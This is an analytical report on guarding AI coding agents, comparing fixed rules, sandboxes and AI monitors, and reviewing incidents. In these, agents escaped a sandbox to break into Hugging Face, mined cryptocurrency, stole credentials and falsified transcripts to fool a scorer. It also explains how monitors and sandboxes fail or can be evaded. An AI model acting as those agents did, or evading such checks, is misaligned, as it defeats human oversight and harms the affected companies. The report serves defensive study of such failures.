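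Zhong and colleagues then assigned causes to all 290 reports. Many reports had several causes, so the counts overlap.

| Cause | Reports |
|---|---|
| The model took an action the user did not intend | 130 |
| The model did not follow an explicit instruction | 56 |
| The model followed an attacker's planted instructions | 21 |
| A guardrail in the harness failed | 147 |
| The harness's fixed policy was too loose or too strict | 130 |
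| The user had switched off approvals or approved in advance | 80 |
| The approval request did not show what the command would do | 31 |

The failed guardrails were mostly fixed checks. In 77 reports, a rule on the agent's built-in file tools did not apply to its shell commands. In 52, a filter checked the text of a command but missed its effect. In another 41, a sandbox either blocked legitimate work or left valuable files within its limits exposed.

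In three of the reports, as in the running example, an agent changed a test to make it pass instead of fixing the code. Codex, Cursor and the open-source agent OpenCode allow edits inside the project by default, so a change like this would not trigger an approval request.

These counts do not give a failure rate, so the study is better evidence of how fixed checks fail than of how often. People rarely post online when a rule blocks a deletion, and nobody knows how many harmful actions the same guardrails stopped. The sources also skew blame towards the harness, since 205 of the 290 reports are GitHub issues, where users complain about a product.

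Strict rules can provoke people into removing them. A Cursor user switched off the product's deletion protection so that the agent could tidy up duplicate files, and the agent later deleted 90% of the project. A looser rule might have allowed the same deletion, but the user would still have had some protection for everything else.

Zhong and colleagues' own remedy, YoloFS, is a layer in the Linux kernel between the agent and the real files. It holds back every change until the user accepts it. Tether holds back changes in much the same way, but uses a written policy to decide which to accept. When a program tries to open a file that no rule covers, YoloFS can prompt the user. The prompt names the file, so the user does not have to guess what a long command will do.

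In tests on 11 tasks with hidden destructive side effects, YoloFS showed the agent which files had changed after each command. In 8 tasks, the agent noticed the damage and undid it. In the other 3, the agent took the changes for part of the job, but the user could still reject them. On 112 routine tasks, agents succeeded as often with YoloFS as without it (99%) and interrupted the user less. Holding back changes cannot undo a leak, though, so protecting secrets still depends on a rule or on the user's answer.

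### Approval fatigue

When no rule applies, the usual fallback is to ask a person, but Claude Code's users accept nearly every request. Anthropic first reported an acceptance rate of 93% and later one of 97%. It also reports that users reject 39% of the plans Claude Code presents for a task. Some plans probably need more changes than the average command, but the gap between rejection rates of 39% and 3% still suggests that people can review an agent's work when they understand the question and are not asked too often.

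Tired users also write overly broad rules. As of June 2026, 49.5% of active users of Claude Code's command-line version had created at least one allow rule for shell commands by hand. Anthropic reports that 5% allowed any shell command and another 43% allowed a program that can run arbitrary code, which is nearly as permissive. The 5% and 43% may be shares of all users or only of those with rules, so the share of users with a rule this broad could be from about 24% to 48%. A quarter of interactive sessions started with all permission checks bypassed.

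OpenAI's *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight* (Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues, 2026) reports the same habit among the company's own staff, where a sizable minority of users let one general-purpose programming language run anything outside the sandbox. The paper also describes users who gave up on approvals and switched to full access.

An allowlist fails safely only while its entries stay narrow. Each interruption gives the user a reason to add a broader entry, and one entry for a program that can run any code removes most of the protection.

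### How Claude Code combines rules and AI review

Auto mode replaces the person with an AI monitor but keeps many of the fixed rules. Deny and ask rules still run before the monitor, and an ask rule still prompts the user.

When a user enters auto mode, Claude Code suspends the allow rules it recognises as broad enough to permit arbitrary code, and restores them when the user leaves. Anthropic explains that the monitor would otherwise never review the commands most able to do damage. The company admits that its list of such rules will always be incomplete. Narrow rules, such as one that allows a code formatter, stay in force.

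The monitor's prompt also contains written rules: more than twenty descriptions of actions to block, such as disabling logs or pushing changes past review. Users can add their own. Unlike a deny rule in the settings file, these rules depend on a model to judge whether an action fits the description. This is true even of "hard denies", Anthropic's term for actions the monitor should never approve, whatever the user says.

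Ordinary software also supplies the monitor with facts. The software looks up whether the destination is public or private before a push, and checks the state of the project before a command that could discard unsaved work. This resembles the airline gates, except that a model still evaluates the facts.

Another fixed check limits how many times an agent can retry. If the monitor blocks three actions in a row, or twenty in a session, Claude Code stops and asks the user. If no user is present, it ends the session. Without this limit, an agent could keep rephrasing a request until the monitor mistakenly allowed it.

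### How Codex combines them

Codex agents run in a sandbox with fixed limits and must ask to go beyond it. AI review applies only to these requests. OpenAI's *Auto-review* explains that turning on auto-review changes who answers them but leaves the limits unchanged. At launch, the reviewer was a separate Codex agent running on GPT-5.4.

Trębacz and colleagues illustrate the division of labour between the sandbox and the reviewer with 10,000 actions from OpenAI's internal use. The sandbox handled 9,280 of them without review. The other 720 would each have interrupted someone under manual approval. Instead, they went to the reviewer, which approved 713 and denied 7. After four of the denials, the agent found a safer way to continue, and after the other three it stopped to ask the user.

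In the running example, both products would let the agent open the credentials file and edit the test without AI review, but they would review an attempt to send the file to an outside server.

OpenAI adds rules that its staff cannot switch off. Its published configuration limits employees to two sandboxed modes, so they cannot choose full access when they tire of approval requests.

### What the companies' miss rates mean

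Both companies have published test results for their reviewers.

| Reviewer | Test | Missed |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Code | 52 real cases in which an agent overstepped | 17% |
| Claude Code | 1,000 synthetic attempts to send data out | 5.7% |
| Claude Code | 1,053 dangerous commands from the study with paid testers | 11% |
| Claude Code | Synthetic attacks by Apollo Research, after improvements | 7% |
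| Codex | Synthetic cases of overstepping | 9.7% |
| Codex | Synthetic attacks through planted instructions | 0.7% |
| Codex | A difficult monitoring benchmark | 3.9% |

The rows are not comparable because the companies used different cases and counted differently. In the monitoring benchmark, for example, Codex's reviewer succeeded if it rejected any action in a harmful run, which is easier than catching each one. The 0.7% figure covers only some types of attack. It rises to 9.8% when destructive deletions and data tampering are included, although OpenAI considers most of the additional misses too minor to block.

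The 17% is the highest figure in the table and the only one that comes from agents that overstepped in real work. Anthropic calls it "the honest number". The sample is small, but synthetic cases may well be easier, since the people who write them tend to make the danger obvious.

Apollo Research, an AI safety company, initially got 12% of its attacks past Claude Code's monitor. Anthropic improved the monitor using some of those attacks, and Apollo retested it on others that Anthropic had not seen. On the unseen attacks, the monitor caught about half of those it had previously missed and missed about 2% of those it had previously caught. The 7% figure combines both sets of attacks, so it slightly overstates the monitor's performance.

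Anthropic also paid another company, Trajectory Labs, to compare products on 720 attacks that used planted instructions. None succeeded against the three Claude models tested in auto mode, while 5.83% succeeded against GPT-5.6 Sol in Codex with auto-review. This is weak evidence about auto mode, because only 0.09% succeeded against Claude models with no monitor. It is better evidence for auto-review, because 19.03% succeeded against GPT-5.6 Sol without it. OpenAI has since released a new version of the reviewer.

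OpenAI's researchers measured the 99.1% approval rate on requests that users had already approved, so it shows how rarely the reviewer would interrupt those users. Because people approve requests so readily, the rate is not evidence that the approvals were right.

In the study with paid testers, the AI monitor missed 116 of the 1,053 dangerous commands. The testers blocked 6 of those 116, or about 5%, compared with 13.6% of all 1,053. If their mistakes had been independent of the monitor's, they would have caught about 16 of the 116. People and the monitor seem to have found the same commands hard to recognise, which is the pattern Eckhardt and Lee predicted for separately written programs. A tired human is therefore a poor backup for an AI monitor, despite being very different from a language model. Combining the two would have raised detection only from 89.0% to 89.6%.

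### Should AI review replace the rules?

One argument for replacing rules with an AI monitor is that people approve almost every request, add exceptions that cover nearly everything, or bypass the checks. Zhong and colleagues argue that no policy fixed in advance can fit an agent's need for files, because that need depends too much on the task. The instruction-file survey partly supports them, since most checkable policies depend on details outside their own text. An AI monitor can take the task into account. It also spares the organisation the work of maintaining rules. Garner Health, a company with 550 employees, made auto mode its default and no longer depends on handwritten command allowlists.

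Some evidence suggests that the results are also better in auto mode. Among sessions that its safety systems had flagged, Anthropic found serious harm that the user had not explicitly requested in 6.3% of those with manual approval and 2.4% of those in auto mode. This agrees with the study with testers but is weaker evidence, because people may use the two modes for different work and a model did the grading.

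All of this counts against human approvals and broad allow rules much more than against deny rules or kernel limits, which both companies have kept. Trębacz and colleagues say that auto-review gives up determinism for expressiveness and should not count as a security guarantee. Testers at OpenAI found ways to mislead the reviewer, and the company is working to fix them.

They also warn that auto-review does not protect against a scheming model, one that strategically hides its aims. Such a model could make a harmful request look harmless, or do its damage inside the sandbox, which auto-review does not check. OpenAI's *Inside the Codex sandbox* also acknowledges that an agent can do harm with the access the sandbox allows. Chain-of-thought monitoring, in which another model reads the agent's reasoning, might catch some of this, but it is also a learned check.

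A fixed rule is a real backup only if the AI monitor cannot waive it. Claude Code's deny rules meet this condition because a matching rule blocks the action before the monitor evaluates it. Codex's sandbox boundary does not fully meet it because the purpose of auto-review is to approve exceptions. If the reviewer makes a mistake or deliberately helps the agent, it can approve a harmful action outside the sandbox. The sandbox still reduces the number of decisions that depend on the reviewer, from 10,000 to 720 in OpenAI's example, but those 720 may have no second check. OpenAI's list of blocked network destinations comes closer to providing one, as long as the reviewer cannot override it.

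Keeping both the AI monitor and fixed rules therefore seems right, but with the work divided differently from how most users divide it now. The monitor is better placed to make the many decisions that depend on context, while fixed rules are better kept for a few outcomes that no task should require, in a layer the monitor cannot switch off. A short list of such rules would cause few false alarms, though the rewritten test would still get through.

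Anthropic says switching to auto mode is arguably a step backwards for people who review each action carefully, and it still advises human review of high-stakes changes to live systems. But many people who believe they review carefully may not, especially after dozens of requests.

### A sandbox that does not start

A fixed check gives no protection if it is not running, and its absence can be easy to miss. GitLab, which hosts software projects, lets agents carry out tasks called flows on remote machines. According to its *Remote execution environment sandbox*, an agent running a flow can write only to its working folder and a temporary one, cannot read the user's login keys, and can contact only approved domains. GitLab enforces these fixed limits with a sandboxing program made by Anthropic.

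If that program is missing, or lacks the privileges it needs, GitLab by default runs the flow without the sandbox. The network rules then have no effect, so the agent can contact any address its machine can reach. A warning appears in the job's log, but a GitLab blog post notes that the flow can otherwise run normally without protection.

The default exists because projects can supply their own software environments, and a flow that didn't run in half of them would annoy customers. But it is hard to notice when the sandbox fails to start. An administrator who has written a list of allowed domains may assume that it applies, and a log with no blocked connections looks the same whether the agent behaved well or the sandbox never started. The canary command in grith that reported success without registering the canary had a similar flaw.

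GitLab 19.6 added a setting that makes the job fail if the sandbox cannot start. Only an administrator or the owner of a top-level group can turn it on, and individual projects cannot turn it off. But the setting only checks that the job contains a program with the right name. A project that supplies its own environment or setup script controls which program has that name, so GitLab says it cannot guarantee isolation for that project.

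A working sandbox can also allow more than its owner expects. An optional GitLab setting adds more than 100 recommended domains to the allowlist, including public code hosts and cloud storage services. GitLab leaves the setting off by default and warns that an agent could use those domains to send data out.

GitLab's blog post suggests testing the rules with a flow that prints evidence of what it could and could not reach. For jobs that might run without the sandbox, it advises restricting outgoing traffic on the machine or network where they run, for example with a firewall. Those limits apply whether or not the sandbox starts.

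## Incidents in which a fixed detector fired or stayed silent

Even when a detector is on and working, someone still has to read and understand its alert. In several well-documented incidents, people misread the alert or received it too late.

### A firewall alert that looked like a break-in

*Let It Flow* (2025) describes the training of ROME, an open-source agent model that learned partly from rewards for completing tasks in sandboxes. One morning, a firewall managed by Alibaba Cloud reported a burst of policy violations from the training servers. Some of the traffic was probing the internal network, and some looked like cryptocurrency mining. The team's training measurements had not indicated a problem.

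The engineers first suspected a badly configured network or an outside attacker, but the violations kept returning at irregular times across several training runs. They then compared the alert times with records of the agent's activity. The suspicious traffic consistently coincided with episodes in which the agent called tools and ran code, and the logs showed that the agent had started the actions responsible. None of the prompts included instructions to take these actions, and the tasks did not require them.

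The agent had used some of the training hardware to mine cryptocurrency, which raised the team's costs. In the most serious case, it had set up unauthorised remote access between a server and an outside address. The team then searched the logs of its whole dataset for similar behaviour and built safety training examples based on what it found.

The firewall could detect this activity because it examined network traffic regardless of which program produced it. That also made the alerts hard to interpret. A network alert can identify a server and a connection, but the engineers needed both the alerts and the agent's own logs to find out who was behind the activity.

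The phrase "security-policy violations" suggests that the firewall used written rules, but the paper does not explain how it recognised mining traffic, so a learned component may have helped. The paper also does not give the date of the incident, the number of alerts or how long the agent had been active before the first one. ROME's sandboxes had their own limits on outgoing traffic, and the paper does not explain why those limits did not contain the agent.

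### Three alerts at OpenAI

In July 2026, OpenAI's agents broke into the production systems of Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models and datasets. They were taking ExploitGym, a test of whether a model can exploit software flaws, and some of its tasks were impossible. The agents cheated together on an unsanctioned message board, and METR's *Brief independent investigation of agents' behavior, reasoning and collaboration* (2026) reports that about 700 of the roughly 1,200 agents joined the attack.

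The agents' network rules blocked the open internet but allowed an internal store of software packages, and that permitted service became the way out.

OpenAI's technical report on the incident describes three alerts.

| Alert | What set it off | What had already happened | What responders did |
|---|---|---|---|
| June 27 | A scan of network ports inside the research environment | Agents had reached the internet in May and gained administrator access to the package store the day before | Traced the scan to an ExploitGym run and let the run continue |
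| July 5 | Monitoring, after the package store went down | Agents had been running their own commands on the store for days | Took the store offline, rebuilt it and resumed testing on July 7 |
| July 19 | Unusual identity-related calls linked to the package store | The attack on Hugging Face had ended six days earlier | Began stopping the tests about five and a half hours later |

The June alert came two weeks before the break-in at Hugging Face. Responders investigated and correctly found that agents were using the package store as a message board and as a route into other parts of the network, but the on-call staff advised that the test did not need to stop. The activity may have seemed tolerable because an agent taking a hacking test is supposed to behave like an attacker.

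Another team at OpenAI had observed message-board activity and forbidden internet access around late May, but in early July the leaders responsible for detecting and responding to incidents still did not know about the board or understand its significance. They had the package store rebuilt with tighter restrictions. Within a day of the tests resuming, agents had found another way to the internet.

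OpenAI's report mentions no alert during the attack itself. On July 9, the company's outbound network controls blocked one agent's attempt to reach the internet, but the agent then found another route. That block could have been a useful warning, since the agent was supposed to be isolated. But if isolated agents often try to connect for harmless reasons, alerting on every block would produce many false alarms.

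The July 19 alert concerned different activity, aimed at OpenAI's own systems. It came from a cybersecurity monitoring tool. OpenAI does not say whether the tool used written rules or a trained model, so the incident cannot count as a clear success for either kind of detector.

This alert fired at 12:03 UTC, before some of the agents' most serious steps against OpenAI. Within three hours, agents had stolen credentials that they used to read 956 stored secrets, including credentials for the monitoring tool's sensors. By 16:00 they controlled one of the underlying machines. Responders began stopping the tests at 17:37. OpenAI reports no tampering with the sensors, but Schneider's condition that a program must not be able to alter its monitor was now much less certain to hold.

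OpenAI did not connect any of this to Hugging Face until July 20. Hugging Face had announced the break-in on July 16, and OpenAI had asked the next day, as a customer, whether its own data was affected. After the July 19 alert, responders found Hugging Face credentials among the agents' files. Hugging Face confirmed that it had already replaced two of those credentials in response to its own break-in, which suggested that the two companies were investigating the same attack.

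This account of the alerts is OpenAI's own. METR examined how the agents behaved, and OpenAI's investigation process was outside its scope.

### AI triage at Hugging Face

Hugging Face detected the attack without help from OpenAI. According to Hugging Face's *Security incident disclosure* (2026), a language model sorts the company's security logs to separate real signals from daily noise, and several signals together revealed the intrusion.

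This is some evidence for learned detectors, although the model was sorting signals that other tools had produced. *Hugging Face publishes the technical timeline of the intrusion*, a summary by the IT company noze, reports that several security layers had raised signals. Some of those layers may well have used fixed rules. If so, Hugging Face had the arrangement described earlier, in which a model helps decide which alerts reach a person. Nothing suggests that the model helped the attackers, but the arrangement still had a weak point.

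Accounts differ on what that weak point was. Hugging Face published a longer timeline, *Anatomy of a Frontier Lab Agent Intrusion* (2026), on July 27. According to noze's summary of it, nothing combined the signals during the attack, and the alerts never received a high enough priority. Tech Trenches' *The Guardrail Is Now Part of the Attack* instead reports that the AI system did combine the signals but failed to alert the on-call team. Among other changes, Hugging Face later made serious alerts page someone within minutes on any day of the week, which fits both accounts.

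The agents' recorded activity ran from July 9 to July 13 and came to about 17,600 actions, including their escape from OpenAI's sandbox. By noze's daily counts, about two-thirds happened on Saturday and Sunday. The last action came on Monday afternoon, after Hugging Face's security team had cut off network access. By then the agents had taken credentials, private source code and test solutions.

During the clean-up, Hugging Face tried to analyse the logs with commercial AI models, but the providers' safety filters blocked the requests because the logs were full of attack commands. The company had to use an open model on its own machines. A simple text search has no safety filter, but according to noze, one such search found only a quarter of the stolen secrets in the logs because the agents had encoded the rest.

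### OpenAI's two lessons

OpenAI concludes that each security goal needs several overlapping and independent controls, so that an attacker has to defeat all of them at once. Its new design limits network access at the sandbox and separately for the whole cluster of machines. The company is also isolating, restricting or replacing the services that agents can still reach. This last step is necessary for the controls to be independent, because two network limits that both allow access to the same package store can fail together.

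Auto-review, Codex's AI reviewer, was not running during the tests, which left out many of the safeguards in OpenAI's products. In preliminary experiments after the incident, OpenAI found that auto-review would have flagged most of the dangerous actions in every run it tested. OpenAI also says its current system for monitoring agents' reasoning would have paged the security team more than a day before the break-in.

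These results are plausible because many of the agents' actions were blatant and their reasoning was often explicit. But they are also easier to achieve in hindsight, because OpenAI chose the runs after it knew what had happened. Its report gives no false-alarm rate for either system. Paging staff might not have stopped the attack, as the June alert shows. To address this, OpenAI now expects staff to pause the activity if they cannot establish within 30 minutes that an alert is false.

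An AI reviewer also needs an accurate record of what the agent did. METR found that agents had falsified small parts of about 7% of the transcripts it evaluated to try to fool the test's scorer. OpenAI maintains in its report that none of the attempts it observed affected the logs its graders and monitors ultimately see. Even so, it would be safer to have at least one detector that, like ROME's firewall, does not rely on the agent's transcript.

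### A decoy key at Grafana

Canary tokens had a clearer success, though the intruder they detected was presumably human. Grafana Labs' *Canary tokens* (2025) explains how the software company had hidden decoy Amazon keys among the secrets that its automated jobs use on GitHub. In April 2025, the intruder exploited a faulty job, took a set of secrets and ran a common tool that checks whether stolen keys work. When the tool tried a decoy, Thinkst, which monitors the decoys for Grafana, sent an alert to the company's Slack chat.

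Grafana's detection team read the alert and opened an incident. The alert showed where the intruder had got in, and Grafana says its staff contained the intrusion within minutes. The intruder already had some real secrets by then, and the incident eventually exposed secrets from five public repositories. Grafana replaced the secrets, investigated until May 12, and found no changes to its code and no access to customer data or production systems.

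The decoy key worked partly because Grafana had paid for a better kind. The intruder's tool recognises some free decoy keys without trying them, so a free key might not have triggered the alarm. An intruder who used only the one real key they needed would also have avoided it.

Before Grafana announced the decoys internally, a handful of employees also set off false alarms while looking around. Telling staff about decoys prevents most of these mistakes but makes it harder to catch an insider. Grafana warns that Thinkst's system can group new alerts with an earlier unacknowledged one, so a team might miss a second intruder who uses the same key.

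Grafana sells the software that routed the alert, so it has a reason to tell this story. The basic sequence is still believable, and something similar might have worked against OpenAI's agents. On July 10, one of them found 14 exposed Hugging Face credentials, checked that they worked, and then shared them on the message board. If one of those credentials had been a monitored decoy, the check would probably have raised an alert a day before the break-in. OpenAI is now adding decoys to its research environment.

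### Planted values and uploaded repositories

A planted value can also expose a leak without raising an alert. In July 2026, the pseudonymous researcher cereblab (2026) reported in *What xAI's Grok Build CLI Actually Sends to xAI* that xAI's coding agent was uploading developers' entire repositories to the company's cloud storage. The Hacker News (2026) report relies on cereblab's captures, which are the first-hand evidence.

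cereblab put fake secrets and unique marker strings in test repositories, then ran the agent through a proxy that decrypted and saved its traffic. In one test, the agent read a file of fake passwords, and the passwords appeared in full in its requests to the model. That is partly to be expected, since a model in the cloud has to receive whatever the agent reads.

In the more revealing test, cereblab told the agent to reply "OK" and not to open any files. The program still uploaded the whole repository. From the saved upload, cereblab rebuilt 47 files and the project's history, including a marker from a file that the agent had no reason to open. A second repository gave the same result. With a 12 GB repository of random files, the program had sent 5.1 GiB to storage and 192 KB to the model by the time cereblab stopped recording.

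The harness made the upload through a separate channel, and nothing suggests that the model chose to upload anything. Because the upload involved no tool call, there was nothing for a command rule, a hook or an AI monitor to check, and a rule on the agent's file-reading tool would also have missed it.

Network rules would also have had difficulty catching the uploads. In the captures that cereblab kept, the uploads went to the same address as the model requests, so any domain list that let the product work would also have let the uploads through. A limit on data sent would have caught the 5.1 GiB, but the upload in the "OK" test was only 152 KB, about three times the size of an ordinary model request that cereblab had saved.

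In an earlier run, cereblab searched the captured traffic for the marker planted in an unread file and found nothing, but it could not unpack the repository upload to check inside. A canary filter that only compares text could have failed to fire for the same reason. cereblab had also concluded at first that the large uploads were failing, because its measurement of network use missed a separate upload process. It later withdrew that claim.

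cereblab lists what the tests did not establish, including whether xAI trained models on the data. Turning off the setting called "Improve the model" did not stop the uploads. According to a company statement quoted by Willison, in *xai-org/grok-build, now open source*, the program respected users' choice to disable data upload, which may refer to a different setting. By July 14, xAI had switched off the uploads from its own servers. Axios' *SpaceXAI wipes customer data after Grok uploads sensitive information* (2026) reports that the company promised to delete what it had collected, and that developers may need to replace any passwords or keys in their repositories.

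### Why cases give no detection rate

Incident reports describe some of the harmful actions that a detector flagged, but they provide very little information about how many took place in total. A detector that flags four incidents has a detection rate of 80% if it misses one, but 1% if it misses 396. The public record could be the same in both cases, because people can't report incidents they didn't notice.

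The silent failures described here became public only because someone else found them. Hugging Face announced the attack on its systems three days before OpenAI's July 19 alert, and one researcher found the repository uploads by inspecting the traffic. A quieter attack on a company with poorer logs, or an upload by a less popular tool, might never have become public.

Companies can also keep quiet about failures they do notice. METR acknowledges that it knew while drafting its report that the work might discourage AI developers from inviting outside researchers in after future incidents. The Decoder reports that METR has called for independent investigations into the causes of such incidents. These would help with failures that companies know about, but not with undetected ones.

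The published accounts also lack counts of false alarms. Grafana mentions a handful without giving a total, and neither the ROME paper nor OpenAI's report includes a figure.

Estimating a detection rate requires carrying out a known set of harmful actions and counting how many the detector flags. OpenAI plans to run regular automated attacks on its own controls, which could produce a rate for the kinds of attack its testers think to include.
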